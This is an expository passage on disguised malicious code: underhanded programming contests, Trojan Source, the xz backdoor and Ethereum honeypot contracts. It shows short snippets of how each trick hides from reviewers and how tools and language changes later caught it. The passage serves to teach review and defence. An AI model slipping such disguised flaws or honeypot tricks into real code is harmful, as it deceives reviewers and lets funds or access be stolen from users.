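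Other entries wrote past the end of a piece of memory, as Blackburn's did. Karen Pease's 2014 winner had a 16-byte buffer for an audit record, enough for four numbers. It recorded the year inside `__isleap`, a leap-year test that looks like a function but is a macro containing three copies of its argument. *2014 Winners* (Craver, 2015) explains that the recording code first checks the clock, which resets the year to 0. All three copies run when the year is 0, so the program records the year three times. Two more numbers follow, and the fifth overwrites the pointer that determines where the program writes next. The final number goes into the user's record and sets the account's creation date to zero, which reveals the surveillance.

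Åkesson's third-place entry from 2008 used a macro that was missing a pair of parentheses. As a result, the macro gave 3 bytes per pixel for `256 > max` and 6 for `max < 256`, although the two conditions are equivalent. The program used one to allocate memory and the other to write its output, so it wrote twice as much as it should have, and the second half was the original image. The macro appeared to support rare images with more color detail, but the program failed on them. The judges' general lesson from this entry was to "make the common case evil, and the uncommon case wrong". A tester who tried one of the rare images would find an ordinary bug and might look no further.

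Some entries exploited format strings, the codes C programs use to describe input and output. In a format for reading text, a line break matches any amount of blank space, including none, although it looks as if it requires a line break. In 2009 Colbus used this to make the program treat part of a clerk's comment as a new luggage record. Frederic Brault's 2013 entry used usernames as formats when printing them, so a user could choose a name containing a code that made the program write to memory.

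Error handling that favors the author was common as well. About a third of the 2015 entrants used NaN ("not a number"), the value a computer stores for an undefined result such as 0/0. Every greater-than or less-than comparison with NaN is false. Peter Eastman's entry ended with this line:

```c
return (correlation < threshold ? 0 : 1);
```

The program rejects the warhead if the correlation is below the threshold and accepts it otherwise. This is the same as accepting a correlation at or above the threshold, except when the correlation is NaN. The comparison is then false, so the program accepts. Acceptance is the default, as cooperation is for CupodBot. NaN entries mostly missed the shortlist, in part because experienced C programmers notice a division with no check for zero. Michael Dunphy added such a check, but because of a missing `&`, it recorded errors in a temporary copy of the error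 flag, and the program then checked the original.

Gaëtan Leurent's 2013 entry contains a check that is correct in the source but missing from the running program. The program computes a number from a username, takes its absolute value, finds the remainder after dividing by 151, and checks that the remainder is not negative. The smallest 32-bit integer, −2,147,483,648, has no positive counterpart, so on typical machines its absolute value comes out negative and the remainder is −2. The check would catch this, but C's rules allow a compiler to assume that an absolute value is never negative. An optimizing compiler therefore deletes the check as redundant, while someone who reviews only the source will think it still runs.

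### How much the results prove

The contest showed that skilled programmers can hide serious misbehavior in fewer than 70 lines of clear code. The 2007 judges said that all the entries they published survived compiler warnings. So even a careful reader may misunderstand a short program. It is much harder to tell how often readers would miss such tricks.

As in Horn's contest, the judges knew that every program was malicious. In 2015, entrants put their explanations in a separate file so that judges could first read the code without knowing the trick. Reviewers at work usually have no warning that code is malicious, and they have many other things to check. They would probably catch less than the judges did, though nobody tested this by giving the entries to unwarned reviewers.

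There are anecdotes of experts struggling with entries even when they knew the code was underhanded. Craver called one 2013 entry confusing even while explaining it, and he stared for some time at a short 2014 program by Domenico Andriole without finding the bug. The second case is weaker evidence because the bug was in a function that Andriole had left out of the file, with only a comment to hint at it.

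The published entries are also an unusual sample. For 2008 the contest named three people out of more than 100 entrants. A 2009 entrant who blogs as jmvalin published a program with three independent ways to misroute a bag, and it does not appear among the contest's results. Most entries that judges found clumsy or obvious have disappeared, so the surviving ones make underhanded code look harder to spot than it typically was. But entrants worked for small prizes. The first was a case of beer, later ones were gift certificates, and the 2015 winner got $1,000. Someone who stood to gain millions could spend far longer on a disguise.

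The judges' taste also affected the selection. They gave points for wit and spite, and in 2007 they chose Colbus's program despite its length because they admired the bug. A real attacker would have no reason to be original, and might do better with an ordinary mistake that reviewers often see.

Like Horn's contest, this one included no honest programs, which is its largest gap. The judges became suspicious when a program divided without checking for zero, masked pixels that it could have erased, or copied a simple list into a complicated structure. Honest programmers do all of these things, and nobody counted how often. A reader who rejected every program with such features might catch many disguised ones, but also reject an unknown share of honest ones. Without the rates at which human readers catch disguised programs and reject honest ones, nobody can tell from the contest whether they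 are accurate enough to make disguise unprofitable in the Prisoner's Dilemma.

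## 2014 to 2024: disguised code in other languages and in real software

The designers of C rarely change rules that existing programs depend on, so the tricks from the Underhanded C Contest still work. Solidity was a young language in 2017, when Nick Johnson organized the first Underhanded Solidity Contest on the same model. Christian Reitwiessner, Solidity's lead developer, was one of the judges, according to the contest announcement that Stalder (2017) reposted. He could therefore change the language after seeing the tricks. The contest returned in 2020, 2022 and 2024.

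### 2017: token sales

The first task was a contract that sells new tokens for ether, Ethereum's currency, and secretly cheats. Many entrants reused one of Solidity's built-in names. At the time `now` stood for the current time and `msg` held details of the current call, such as who had made it. A contract could declare its own variable with the same name, which hid ("shadowed") the built-in one:

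```solidity
uint now = 0;              // hides the built-in clock

require(now < saleEnd);    // always true, so the sale never ends
```

If these lines are far apart, someone who reads only the second will assume that it checks the clock. Solidity's developers had added warnings about shadowing shortly before the contest, but Wheeler quotes Reitwiessner as saying that the solution was not yet complete. Solidity's *0.7.0 Release Announcement* (2020) records that the developers removed `now` from the language. Programmers have written `block.timestamp` since then.

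Richard Moore came second with a trick that is harder to remove. The contract's description, *Underhanded Solidity Contest Entry*, promises buyers that the owner can withdraw only 1 ether in the first week, 2 in the next, then 4, then 8. Each limit is the total withdrawn so far plus one. The trick works because a contract cannot refuse ether, as ConsenSys Diligence's *2nd Solidity Underhanded Contest* (2020) explains. A contract can include a function to record incoming payments, but some ways of sending ether bypass that function.

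Suppose a contract calculates past withdrawals by subtracting its current balance from the ether it collected. If the owner forces in 2 extra ether before withdrawing anything, the result is −2, and the limit is −1. Solidity's unsigned numbers cannot be negative, and in 2017 they wrapped around, so −1 became a 78-digit number and the owner could take everything. Reitwiessner called unrecorded payments "quite tricky" to tackle through the language. Many legitimate contracts also read their own balance, so warning about all of them would cause many false alarms.

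### 2020: upgrade mechanisms

Developers cannot edit a contract's bytecode once it is on the blockchain. To be able to fix bugs later, they can give users the address of a proxy, a small contract that forwards each call to a second contract. They upgrade by pointing the proxy to a new contract. Anyone who controls upgrades can therefore replace legitimate code with code that steals users' funds. Entrants to the 2020 Underhanded Solidity Contest had to hide a flaw in such an upgrade mechanism (Heintel, 2020, *The Underhanded Solidity Contest is back!*), and 16 entries qualified.

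Robert Forster's winning contract appears to give users a month's notice of any upgrade, enough time to withdraw their money. *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest* (Heintel, 2020) includes comments by Reitwiessner, who found only one feature of the contract suspicious. It stored the date as a day and a month instead of a single timestamp.

The trick depends on invisible characters. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, has special characters for mixing left-to-right scripts like English with right-to-left ones like Hebrew. The right-to-left override (RLO) makes an editor display the text after it backwards, until a character called PDF ends the effect. Solidity never accepted these characters in instructions, but it did accept them in comments, which begin with `/*` and end with `*/`. In this simplified version, the names in braces stand for the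 invisible characters:

```text
stored:   setDate(/*{RLO}*/ d , m /*{PDF}*/);
shown:    setDate(/**/ m , d /**/);
```

The compiler reads the stored text, so it skips the two comments and passes `d` and then `m` to `setDate`. An editor displays everything between the invisible characters in reverse. A reversed `*/` is `/*`, so both comments still look complete, but `d` and `m` change places. If `setDate` expects the month first, the call looks right on screen but passes the arguments in the wrong order.

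Swapping the day and month turns 2 December into 12 February. For an upgrade proposed on 2 November, that date has already passed, so the owner could switch to the new code long before users expect it.

Security researchers had shown the same trick in Solidity at a conference in 2019. They also added a check for it to Slither, a static analysis tool, according to Packet Storm's *Ethereum Smart Contracts Exploitation Using Right To Left Override Character*. The character has very few legitimate uses, as SWC Registry's *Right-To-Left-Override control character (U+202E)* notes. A tool can therefore flag every occurrence with few false positives.

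Solidity's developers responded within two weeks of the results. Their *0.7.6 Release Announcement* (2020) says the compiler now rejects any comment or Unicode string that changes the text direction without restoring it before the end. The contract in the example above would no longer compile, because its first comment ends while the override is still active.

Jaime Iglesias came second with a contract that its admin is supposed to be able to upgrade only with the owner's consent. Ethereum keeps a contract's data in numbered slots, and this contract records the consent in a slot whose number has 64 hexadecimal digits. According to a comment, the number is the hash of a standard phrase, which would make the slot practically unique. It is actually the number of the slot that holds the token balance of an address known to the admin. When the admin sends tokens to that address, the balance is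 no longer zero, and the contract treats this as the owner's consent. Moving the tokens away cancels the consent. A reader can discover the trick by recalculating the hash, but no compiler check would have caught it, because the compiler accepts any slot number and ignores comments.

Chris Whinfrey received an honorable mention for a contract that relied on users' trust in audits. The judges commented that an audit of an upgradeable contract doesn't matter unless someone also checks every later upgrade. This problem doesn't arise in the program games described earlier, because players cannot change their programs after submitting them.

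### 2022: a decentralized exchange

Entrants in the third contest had to write a decentralized exchange, which is a contract that lets people trade tokens without a company in between. Tynan Richards won with one that holds a pool of two tokens. Users called liquidity providers supply the tokens, and the admin takes a share of the pool's trading fees.

The code seems to protect the providers from a greedy admin. Before the admin's share changes, the contract should pay out past earnings at the old rate. It should then block further claims for seven days, so that providers can leave before the new rate costs them anything. ChainSecurity's *Beware of Undefined Behavior!* (2022) prints the code, and these are the important lines, slightly shortened:

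```solidity
event AdminFeeChanged(uint256 indexed oldFee, uint256 indexed newFee);

function changeAdminFees(uint256 newAdminFee) external onlyAdmin {
    emit AdminFeeChanged(retireOldAdminFee(), setNewAdminFee(newAdminFee));
}
```

`emit` writes an entry in the blockchain's log, and the contract has to run two functions to fill it in. `retireOldAdminFee` pays the admin, starts the seven-day wait and returns the old rate, while `setNewAdminFee` stores the new rate. Most programmers will expect the function on the left to run first.

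Solidity's documentation says that the order is unspecified. The compiler usually works from left to right, but in log entries it evaluates values marked `indexed`, which makes them searchable, from right to left. The contract therefore does this:

1. `setNewAdminFee` stores the new rate.
2. `retireOldAdminFee` pays the admin's past earnings at the new rate. The wait has not started, so nothing blocks the payment.
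3. The seven-day wait begins.

Suppose the pool holds 1,000 of each token and has earned 10 of each since the admin's last claim. At a rate of 10%, the admin should get 1 of each. But the contract doesn't cap the rate, so the admin can set it to 10,000% and receive 1,000 of each, which empties the pool.

According to *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2022* (Heintel, 2022), none of the eight judges found the trick before opening the file in which Richards explained it. They knew the contract was malicious and found at least seven other weaknesses, including calculations that could lose precision. An auditor who reported those seven would have seemed thorough while missing the trick. This is stronger evidence that experts can miss disguised code, even when they are looking for it, than the anecdotes from the C contest. But it comes from one program out of 18, and the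 judges chose that program partly because it had fooled them.

Running the contract would have been a better way to find the flaw than reading it. Heintel's announcement says that a good unit test would find it, and so would a fuzzer, a tool that tries many generated inputs. A tester only has to change the fee and check how much the admin receives. The log also contains a clue, since every entry shows the same rate twice. The new rate has already replaced the old one by the time `retireOldAdminFee` returns the "old" rate.

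The same source code does what it appears to do under a different compiler setting. Solidity's newer compilation method, via-IR, is designed to evaluate everything from left to right. ChainSecurity, where Richards worked, points out that log entries then behave as a reader would expect. Solidity's *Releases* shows that the developers called via-IR ready for production in version 0.8.13, but Solidity's *Version 0.8.37*, from September 2026, still lists it separately from the default. A reader therefore needs the compiler settings as well as the source to know what Richards's contract does. A program game likewise needs a rule for how to run the players' programs, or two readers could correctly predict different moves from the same text.

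Solidity's developers could close this loophole by fixing the order of evaluation, but they could do much less about Michael Zhu's third-place entry. Zhu's contract lets people bid ordinary tokens for NFTs, which are unique digital items. It labels each bid by combining the addresses of the NFT and the payment token with an operation called XOR. XOR gives the same result in either order, so swapping the two addresses produces the same label, despite a comment in the code claiming that finding another matching pair is practically impossible. Both kinds of token also use the same command for transfers. Someone who accepts a bid with the addresses swapped can therefore make the contract take an NFT from the bidder instead of the payment. Each instruction follows Solidity's rules, and a compiler cannot detect the flaw in the label without information about its purpose.

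Gerard Persoon won the 2024 contest, which was about transient storage, a new kind of memory that Ethereum erases after each transaction. Solidity programmers could then use this memory only through low-level assembly, and the rules in Solidity's *Underhanded Solidity Contest 2024* warned that assembly without a clear reason looks suspicious. Entrants had a clear reason because the task required assembly, which illustrates how a new feature can make an unusual style of code acceptable before reviewers have learned the feature's pitfalls.

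### Comments that reassure

Zhu's comment discouraged readers from examining the label. Entrants in the 2015 JavaScript Misdirection Contest used comments in a similar way. Peter Jaric, who ran the contest, asked for a program that generates a key and secretly sends it to another computer. Of the 40 entries, 34 were valid. *Spotting Malicious Code Hidden in Plain Sight* (Mann, 2015) describes an entry that disguised assignments as comparisons, as the two lines in the Linux kernel did.

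Wheeler's survey quotes Jaric's observations about the rest. Many contestants put their malicious code in Base64, an encoding that turns any data into letters, digits and a few symbols, and often presented the result as a key or a random seed. Real keys look like this too, so reviewers may not think to decode it. More than one entrant added a link to Stack Overflow, a site where programmers answer each other's questions. Programmers often leave such links to explain unusual code, and Jaric admitted finding it easier to skip code with a good comment above it.

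Wheeler also describes a Python sample that exploits what readers know about other languages. In many languages `//` starts a comment, but in Python it means division, so the text after it runs. Wheeler opened the file in an editor with syntax coloring, which shows this text as code, and did not notice the difference.

### Flaws for specialists

In 2014, Adam Caudill and Taylor Hornby started the Underhanded Crypto Contest, in which entrants hid weaknesses in cryptography. In *on the underhanded crypto contest*, Caudill (2015) hoped that the entries would become training material for reviewers. The first contest had 16 entries, according to the organizers' slides (Caudill, Hornby and Arcieri, *The Underhanded Crypto Contest*). John Meacham, who had won the C contest six years earlier, won it with an encryption program that can compute its key from the wrong piece of memory.

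Gaëtan Leurent was the runner-up with a login protocol that counts the ones in binary numbers. Leurent's "improved" counting function returns 0 for a number with exactly 63 ones. If the numbers are 64 bits long, only 64 of about 18 quintillion possible values trigger the error. Random testing would have exposed Richards's exchange, but it will almost never find one of these values. An attacker who knows about the flaw can use it to break the protocol.

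A smaller contest in 2015 asked for a change to GnuPG, a widely used encryption program, that would leak the user's private key. The winner, Joseph Birr-Pixton, exploited the way GnuPG 1.4 creates DSA signatures. Each signature needs a new random number, and anyone who can guess that number can work out the private key. GnuPG picks a number and checks whether it is below a limit. If it is too large, the program replaces only the first 32 bits and tries again. Slides from the Underhanded Crypto Contest show that Birr-Pixton added this line wherever the program rejects a number:

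```c
memset(rndbuf, 0, nbytes);
```

The line overwrites the rejected number with zeros, but GnuPG was about to reuse most of that number. The next attempt therefore consists of 32 random bits followed by zeros, which leaves at most about 4 billion possibilities, few enough for a computer to try them all. A reviewer who doesn't know how DSA works can understand every word of the line and still approve it. They might even welcome the change, because programmers are supposed to erase secrets they no longer need. Wheeler concluded from such entries that specialists have to review cryptographic code in depth.

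### Trojan Source

In November 2021 the paper *Trojan Source* described attacks that use invisible text-direction characters as a problem for programming languages in general. *Hiding Vulnerabilities in Source Code* (Schneier, 2021) reports that many developers of compilers, editors and code-hosting sites added defenses in the 99 days before the paper's publication.

*SECURITY*, a bug report (Eskola, 2021), shows that the attack also worked in the D programming language. The example appears to compare a variable with the word "safe", followed by an ordinary comment, but the compiler treats the comment as part of the quoted text. The variable contains only "safe", so the two never match, and the program always behaves as if it were in another mode.

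The paper also exposed a gap in Solidity's defense. The 2020 fix rejects a change of text direction that continues past the end of a comment. But some direction characters, called isolates, can make part of a comment appear elsewhere on the line, where it looks like code, even if the comment restores the direction properly. In response to Forster's entry, chriseth (2020) had started a developers' discussion titled *Re-evaluate unicode tricks in comments*. One developer confirmed the gap there in February 2023 and opened a separate issue about it. An automatic process closed the discussion that May for inactivity. Foundry's *Right-to-left override character* describes a stricter check that flags all such direction characters in a Solidity file.

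Code editors can also solve the problem by changing how they display programs. According to a document from the Unicode Consortium, Visual Studio always arranges a program's words and symbols from left to right. This protects people who read code without compiling it. CliqueBot and DupocBot don't need this protection because they work from the stored characters. Language models also receive the stored characters, and researchers have since tested whether the models detect invisible ones.

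### The xz backdoor

On 29 March 2024, Andres Freund reported a backdoor in xz, a file compression package that many Linux systems include. The backdoor targeted SSH, which administrators use to log in to other machines. Freund thought it probably let an attacker in without a valid login (Freund 2024, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*).

Freund was investigating odd behavior in SSH, not reviewing xz's code. Over several weeks, SSH logins on a development version of Debian Linux had used a surprising amount of processor time. Valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory, had also reported errors. A rejected login took 0.807 seconds with the backdoor and 0.299 seconds without it. Freund recorded which instructions ran in each case and traced the point where they diverged to liblzma, a library that belongs to xz. SSH does not use liblzma itself, but Debian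 and some other distributions modify SSH in a way that loads it.

The backdoor got into SSH in four steps:

1. Someone added two files to xz's public repository, supposedly as test data. They contained most of the backdoor in scrambled form.
2. The release packages, which distributions use to build xz, contained an extra line in a build script. It extracted a hidden program from the test files and ran it.
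3. The hidden program checked whether it was part of a Debian or RPM package build on 64-bit Linux. If so, it built the backdoor into liblzma.
4. When the SSH server started, the backdoor searched the computer's memory for a function that checks login keys, and redirected it to its own code. This search caused the delay.

Hackaday's *Security Alert* (2024) points out that the line in step 2 was missing from the repository, so someone reviewing the code there would have found nothing wrong. The test files were in the repository, but people do not read compressed data. Damaged files are also useful for testing a compression program, and one of these was called `bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz`. A reviewer could have asked what the files were for, and Freund found that no test in version 5.6.0 used them. The same question would have exposed the pointless error check in the Linux kernel.

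Comparing the release package with the repository would have revealed the extra line, much as the nightly comparison revealed the kernel change in 2003. But release packages often contain automatically generated build files that are not in the repository, so a difference is not necessarily suspicious. Approval records would not have helped either, because someone with permission made the changes. Freund considered it unlikely that an intruder had taken over this person's computer, since the same person had discussed supposed fixes on several mailing lists. Version 5.6.1 included changes to work around crashes and Valgrind errors that the backdoor had caused.

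The hidden program was obfuscated rather than underhanded, because anyone who unpacked it would have had reason to reject it immediately. Its author made the surrounding files look ordinary so that nobody would unpack it.

To avoid observation at run time, the backdoor also stayed inactive if it found certain debugging tools or a setting called `TERM`, which is normally present when a person starts a program from a terminal. When Freund first started the SSH server by hand, the delay disappeared. A program that behaves well only in a simulation likewise exploits a difference between test conditions and normal use. These checks did not hide the delay during normal logins, where Freund had first noticed it. By then, most distributions that had adopted the affected versions had included them only in pre-release systems.

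## 2017 and 2018: Ethereum contracts that trap their attackers

Starting in January 2017, some Ethereum programmers published honeypot contracts, which use an apparent flaw as bait. The contest entrants and whoever wrote the xz backdoor, by contrast, wanted readers to find nothing wrong.

Torres, Steichen and State (2019), in *The Art of The Scam*, were the first to study honeypots systematically. They define a honeypot as a contract that appears to leak its funds to anyone who sends it more, but traps whatever they send, so that at most its creator can get it out. A honeypot works in three phases:

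1. The creator puts the contract on the blockchain and deposits some ether as bait.
2. A victim sends the required ether, tries to exploit the apparent flaw, and fails.
3. The creator withdraws the bait and the victim's ether.

Anyone with an Ethereum account and enough ether for the bait can set up a honeypot. The creator also needs potential attackers to read the contract, and few people read bytecode. *A Data Science Approach for Detecting Honeypots in Ethereum* (Camino, Torres and colleagues, 2019) notes that creators often published their source code on Etherscan, a website for looking up contracts and transactions, so that people would find the "vulnerable" contract. Etherscan compiles the source and confirms that it produces the bytecode stored on the blockchain, which probably made the contracts look more trustworthy.

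### Why bait works

A honeypot succeeds if readers think its code has a flaw they can profit from. According to Torres and colleagues, the victim concentrates on the apparent flaw and doesn't consider that there may be another. Finding a flaw gives readers a reason to stop looking and seems to explain anything else in the code that looks odd. Something similar happened by accident in the 2022 Solidity contest, where the judges found at least seven weaknesses in Richards's exchange and missed the real trick.

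Contest entrants usually try to look like competent programmers who made one excusable mistake. Honeypots, by contrast, almost always look like a beginner's work, according to the abstract of a 2018 ToorCon talk, *Smart Contract Honeypots for Profit (and probably Fun)*, which adds that it is "still easy to con someone who thinks they're a conman". A reader who takes the author for a beginner is unlikely to suspect a clever trap.

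Plausible deniability matters less to a honeypot's creator than to a programmer who wants to keep a job. By the time the victim understands the trick, the creator has the money, and an Ethereum account does not reveal its owner's name.

Torres and colleagues found eight techniques in 24 honeypots that people had described online. They grouped the techniques by whether the victim misunderstands the virtual machine that runs Ethereum's bytecode, the Solidity compiler, or the Etherscan website.

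### The virtual machine

Only one technique, balance disorder, depends on the virtual machine. This is the main function of a honeypot called MultiplicatorX3:

```solidity
function multiplicate(address adr) payable {
    if (msg.value >= this.balance)
        adr.transfer(this.balance + msg.value);
}
```

`msg.value` is the ether that the user sends with the call, and `this.balance` is the ether that the contract holds. It seems that anyone who sends at least as much as the contract holds will get their ether back, along with everything in the contract.

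Suppose the contract holds 1 ether and a user sends 1 more:

1. Ethereum adds the payment to the contract's balance before it runs the function, so the balance is now 2.
2. The `if` line compares 1 with 2, and the test fails.
3. The function ends without an error, and the contract keeps the user's ether.

Sending more ether doesn't help. If the attacker sends 10 ether, the test compares 10 with 11. The test can succeed only if the contract was empty before the payment, in which case there is nothing to steal.

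The last line encourages the mistake, because adding `msg.value` to `this.balance` makes sense only if the balance does not yet include the payment. The balance already includes it, so the sum counts the payment twice, and the contract would have to pay out 3 ether when it has 2. A reader who did this calculation would see that the payout could never go through.

### The compiler

The most common compiler trick among the confirmed honeypots was inheritance disorder. A Solidity contract can inherit code from another contract, which programmers write with the word `is`. KingOfTheHill, slightly shortened, inherits from a contract called Ownable:

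```solidity
contract Ownable {
    address owner = msg.sender;
    modifier onlyOwner { require(msg.sender == owner); _; }
}

contract KingOfTheHill is Ownable {
    address public owner;

    function() public payable {        // runs when someone sends ether
        if (msg.value > jackpot) owner = msg.sender;
        jackpot += msg.value;
    }
    function takeAll() public onlyOwner {
        msg.sender.transfer(this.balance);
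        jackpot = 0;
    }
}
```

`msg.sender` is the address that makes the current call. When the creator deploys the contract, the first line of Ownable stores the creator's address as `owner`. It looks as if anyone who sends more than the jackpot becomes the new owner and can then call `takeAll`, which only the owner may use.

However, the code declares `owner` twice, and the compiler creates two separate variables. The security researchers dawu and 0x7F (2018), in *以太坊蜜罐智能合约分析* (an analysis of Ethereum honeypot contracts), distinguish the two variables in a similar honeypot by renaming them `owner1` and `owner2`. With those names, a large payment to KingOfTheHill changes `owner2`, the variable in the lower contract. But `takeAll` uses the check from Ownable, which reads `owner1`, and `owner1` still holds the creator's address. Victims who look up the contract's public `owner` variable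 after paying will find their own address.

The full contract also made the winner wait five days before calling `takeAll`, so victims couldn't discover the problem immediately by trying to withdraw. Other players could pay in during the wait.

A 2018 HackerNoon article by Alex Sherbachev describes ICO_Hold, which combines the same duplicated-variable trick with two apparent flaws. Anyone can call a function that seems to make them the owner, and the contract never subtracts withdrawals from a user's recorded deposit. An attacker would therefore expect to deposit 0.5 ether, become the owner and withdraw the deposit repeatedly, but the duplicated variable makes the withdrawal fail.

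The technique that Torres and colleagues call skip empty string literal exploits a bug in old versions of the compiler. A honeypot called DividendDistributor pays its investors through a function with four inputs:

```solidity
function loggedTransfer(uint amount, bytes32 message,
                        address target, address currentOwner)

this.loggedTransfer(amount, "", msg.sender, owner);
```

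The second statement appears to send `amount` to the investor, `msg.sender`, with an empty message. The buggy compiler left out the empty string, so every later value moved up one place. The investor's address became the message, and the owner's address became the target. As bait, the contract seems to let investors withdraw more than they put in, but every withdrawal goes to the owner. A reader who applies Solidity's rules correctly can still misread this contract unless they check the compiler version against a list of known bugs.

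In type deduction overflow, the compiler chooses a type that is too small. A honeypot called For_Test calculates its payment with this loop:

```solidity
for (var i = 0; i < 2 * msg.value; i++) {
    multi = i * 2;
    if (multi < amountToTransfer) break;
    amountToTransfer = multi;
}
```

The loop seems to build up a payment larger than the amount the user sent. Solidity counts ether in wei, and one ether is 10¹⁸ wei, so `i` would have to become enormous. But because `i` is declared with `var`, the compiler gives it the smallest type that can hold its starting value, 0, which is an 8-bit number with a maximum of 255. Doubling `i` gives 254 when `i` is 127, but at 128 the result wraps around to 0 instead of reaching 256. Since 0 is less than 254, the loop stops, and a user who sent more than 0.1 ether gets 254 wei back. Dawu and 0x7F give the payment as 510 wei, which would be right if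 only `i` wrapped around and the multiplication did not.

The last compiler technique, called uninitialised struct, overwrites a variable that the victim has already checked. A struct is a group of variables under one name. In old versions of Solidity, a struct declared inside a function without a starting value pointed to the beginning of the contract's storage, so anything the function wrote to it replaced the contract's first variables.

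Players of CryptoRoulette pay 0.1 ether to guess a secret number, and a correct guess is supposed to win everything in the contract. The code marks the number `private`, but anyone can read the data that a contract stores on the blockchain. This looks like a beginner's mistake that lets a player look up the number and submit it. But before checking the guess, the contract records the player's address in an uninitialised struct, which overwrites the secret number with the address, so the correct guess no longer matches. The contract also rejects guesses above 10, which stops players from submitting their own address as a number. Dawu and 0x7F found that this limit is a further trick. The secret number was between 1 and 20, so half the time nobody could have won even without the overwriting.

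OpenAddressLottery uses the same bug, but the owner has to trigger it. The contract gives each player a 0 or a 1, and players with the lucky number, initially 1, win 1.9 times their stake. A function that only the owner can call picks new random data, "for testing purposes" according to a comment. The lottery can pay out normally until the owner calls this function, which overwrites the lucky number with a multiple of 7 so that nobody can win.

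Solidity's developers have closed most of these routes. Since version 0.5.0 the compiler has rejected `var` and uninitialised structs, and later versions reject two stored variables with the same name in related contracts. But creators can still choose an old compiler, and contracts already on the blockchain do not change.

### The block explorer

The remaining techniques take advantage of readers who trust what Etherscan shows them. The most common is hidden state update. A honeypot called Gift_1_ETH pays its whole balance to anyone who knows a password, and stores only the password's hash. It also seems to let users replace the password:

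```solidity
bool passHasBeenSet = false;

function SetPass(bytes32 hash) payable {
    if (!passHasBeenSet && (msg.value >= 1 ether))
        hashPass = hash;
}
```

A reader will plan to send 1 ether with the hash of a new password and then collect the balance. One Twitter user published a script to do this. The plan fails because the creator has already called another function in the contract that sets `passHasBeenSet` to true, so `SetPass` keeps the ether without changing the password.

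Etherscan's list of transactions would normally show such a call, but it omitted calls from one contract to another that carried no ether. The creator made the change through a second contract, so the call did not appear in the list. Nothing is hidden in the source code, but the reader has to look up the variable's current value on the blockchain, just as players of CryptoRoulette looked up the secret number.

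Hidden transfer conceals part of the source. Etherscan used to display code in a box that did not wrap long lines, so anything past the right edge was invisible until the reader scrolled sideways. Torres and colleagues describe a honeypot that works roughly like this:

```text
function withdrawAll() payable {
    (ordinary check);   {long run of spaces}   if (block.number > 5040270 && msg.sender != owner) throw;
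    msg.sender.transfer(this.balance);
}
```

A reader who doesn't scroll sees a function that gives the contract's whole balance to anyone who calls it. Code off-screen to the right cancels the call unless the caller is the owner. Victims lose the ether they had to pay in before trying to withdraw the balance.

The block number is a trigger. Ethereum numbers its blocks in order, and the main network had already passed block 5,040,270. A careful reader might first copy the contract to a test network, where ether has no value, and try the exploit there. The test networks had shorter chains that were still below that number, so the hidden check stayed off and the exploit worked. The reader then had apparently good evidence that it would work with real money. The contract's creator predicted this test and made sure it succeeded, whereas testers in Horn's contest had no particular reason to try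 election day.

A simpler example, WhaleGiveaway1, has no such trigger. A hidden instruction sends the whole balance to the owner, and then the visible line sends the remaining balance, which is zero, to the user. GitHub did not wrap long lines either, so people studying the contract there could miss the hidden instruction. It is visible in any editor that wraps lines.

In a straw man contract, the code that readers see is not the code that runs. Private_Bank, lightly rewritten here, lets users deposit ether and withdraw it again:

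```solidity
function Private_Bank(address _log) {    // runs once, at creation
    TransferLog = Log(_log);
}

function CashOut(uint amount) {
    if (amount > balances[msg.sender]) return;
    bool paid = msg.sender.call.value(amount)();    // sends the ether
    if (paid) {
        balances[msg.sender] -= amount;
        TransferLog.AddMessage("CashOut");
    }
}
```

The bait is a famous flaw called reentrancy, which an attacker used in 2016 to rob The DAO, an investment fund on Ethereum. `CashOut` sends the ether before it reduces the user's recorded balance. If the user is itself a contract, receiving ether runs its code, and that code can call `CashOut` again before the recorded balance changes. By repeating this, an attacker should be able to empty the bank.

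Suppose the bank holds 5 ether:

1. The victim writes an attacking contract and uses it to deposit 1 ether.
2. The attacking contract calls `CashOut`, receives 1 ether, and calls `CashOut` again each time it is paid.
3. When the payments stop, the bank tries to record the withdrawal by calling `AddMessage("CashOut")`.
4. `AddMessage` cancels the withdrawal, which undoes all the payments. The deposit from step 1 stays in the bank.

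The published file contains a harmless contract called `Log`, whose `AddMessage` function only stores the message. But the bank calls a different contract, at an address its creator supplied, which lets deposits through and cancels every withdrawal except the creator's. Etherscan confirms that the bank's own bytecode matches its source, but does not check the contracts that the bank calls. A reader who recompiles the source and compares the bytecode will therefore find no discrepancy. Trying the published file on a test network would probably mislead the reader too, because they would naturally connect the bank to the harmless `Log`.

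In a variant called firstTest, the outside code can change the caller's variables. The contract appears to record an event and then send its balance to the user. Dawu and 0x7F decompiled the bytecode behind the supposed event log and found that it replaced the user's address with the contract's own, so the contract sent the balance to itself.

The eight techniques do not cover every honeypot. Camino and colleagues later found two more techniques, and *Ethereum Contract Honeypot Risk Analysis* (Ishimaki and Omote, 2022) reports three contracts that put the payment behind the condition `if(1==2)`.

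### When a successful test is part of the trap

Testing on a private copy of the main network in its current state is better than testing on a separate network. The copy has the real block number, stored values and contract behind `Log`, so trying the whole exploit there should expose any of the eight techniques. The test can still fail to expose the trap if the creator changes something between the test and the real payment, as the owner of OpenAddressLottery could.

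Wallet developers later began simulating users' transactions before sending them. Zengo's *Security vulnerability in popular web3 transaction simulation solutions* describes how a contract can detect a simulation and behave harmlessly during it.

Even small trials with real money can mislead. The Block's *Notorious 'jaredfromsubway' MEV bot drained for roughly $7.5 million in counter-MEV honeypot* (2026) reports that in June 2026 an attacker took about $7.5 million from jaredfromsubway, an automated trading program on Ethereum. The program profited at other traders' expense by buying a token just before their trades and selling it just after. The attacker set up 66 fake tokens and priced them so that trading them looked profitable.

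To trade, the program had to give the attacker's contracts permission to take a certain amount of its real tokens. In small trades, the contracts used up the permission and returned a profit. *The Predator Becomes the Prey*, by the security firm Blockaid, describes one in which the program put in about 0.602 WETH (a token worth the same as ether) and got back about 0.603. In larger trades, the contracts left the permission unused. These open permissions eventually reached about 92 WETH each, and the attacker used them all in a single transaction. A developer quoted by The Block called the mechanism a "block-armed switch". As with the hidden transfer honeypot, the author knew how the victim would test the contracts and made them behave well in those tests.

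### Victims, timing and profits

Torres and colleagues searched more than 2 million contracts created up to October 2018 with HoneyBadger, a detection tool they had built, and confirmed 282 honeypots by reading the source code. Creators deployed seven honeypots a month on average, with a peak of 66 in February 2018. Slides by Torres and colleagues give the number of contracts that caught at least one victim:

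| Technique | Confirmed honeypots | Caught a victim | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balance disorder | 20 | 7 | 35% |
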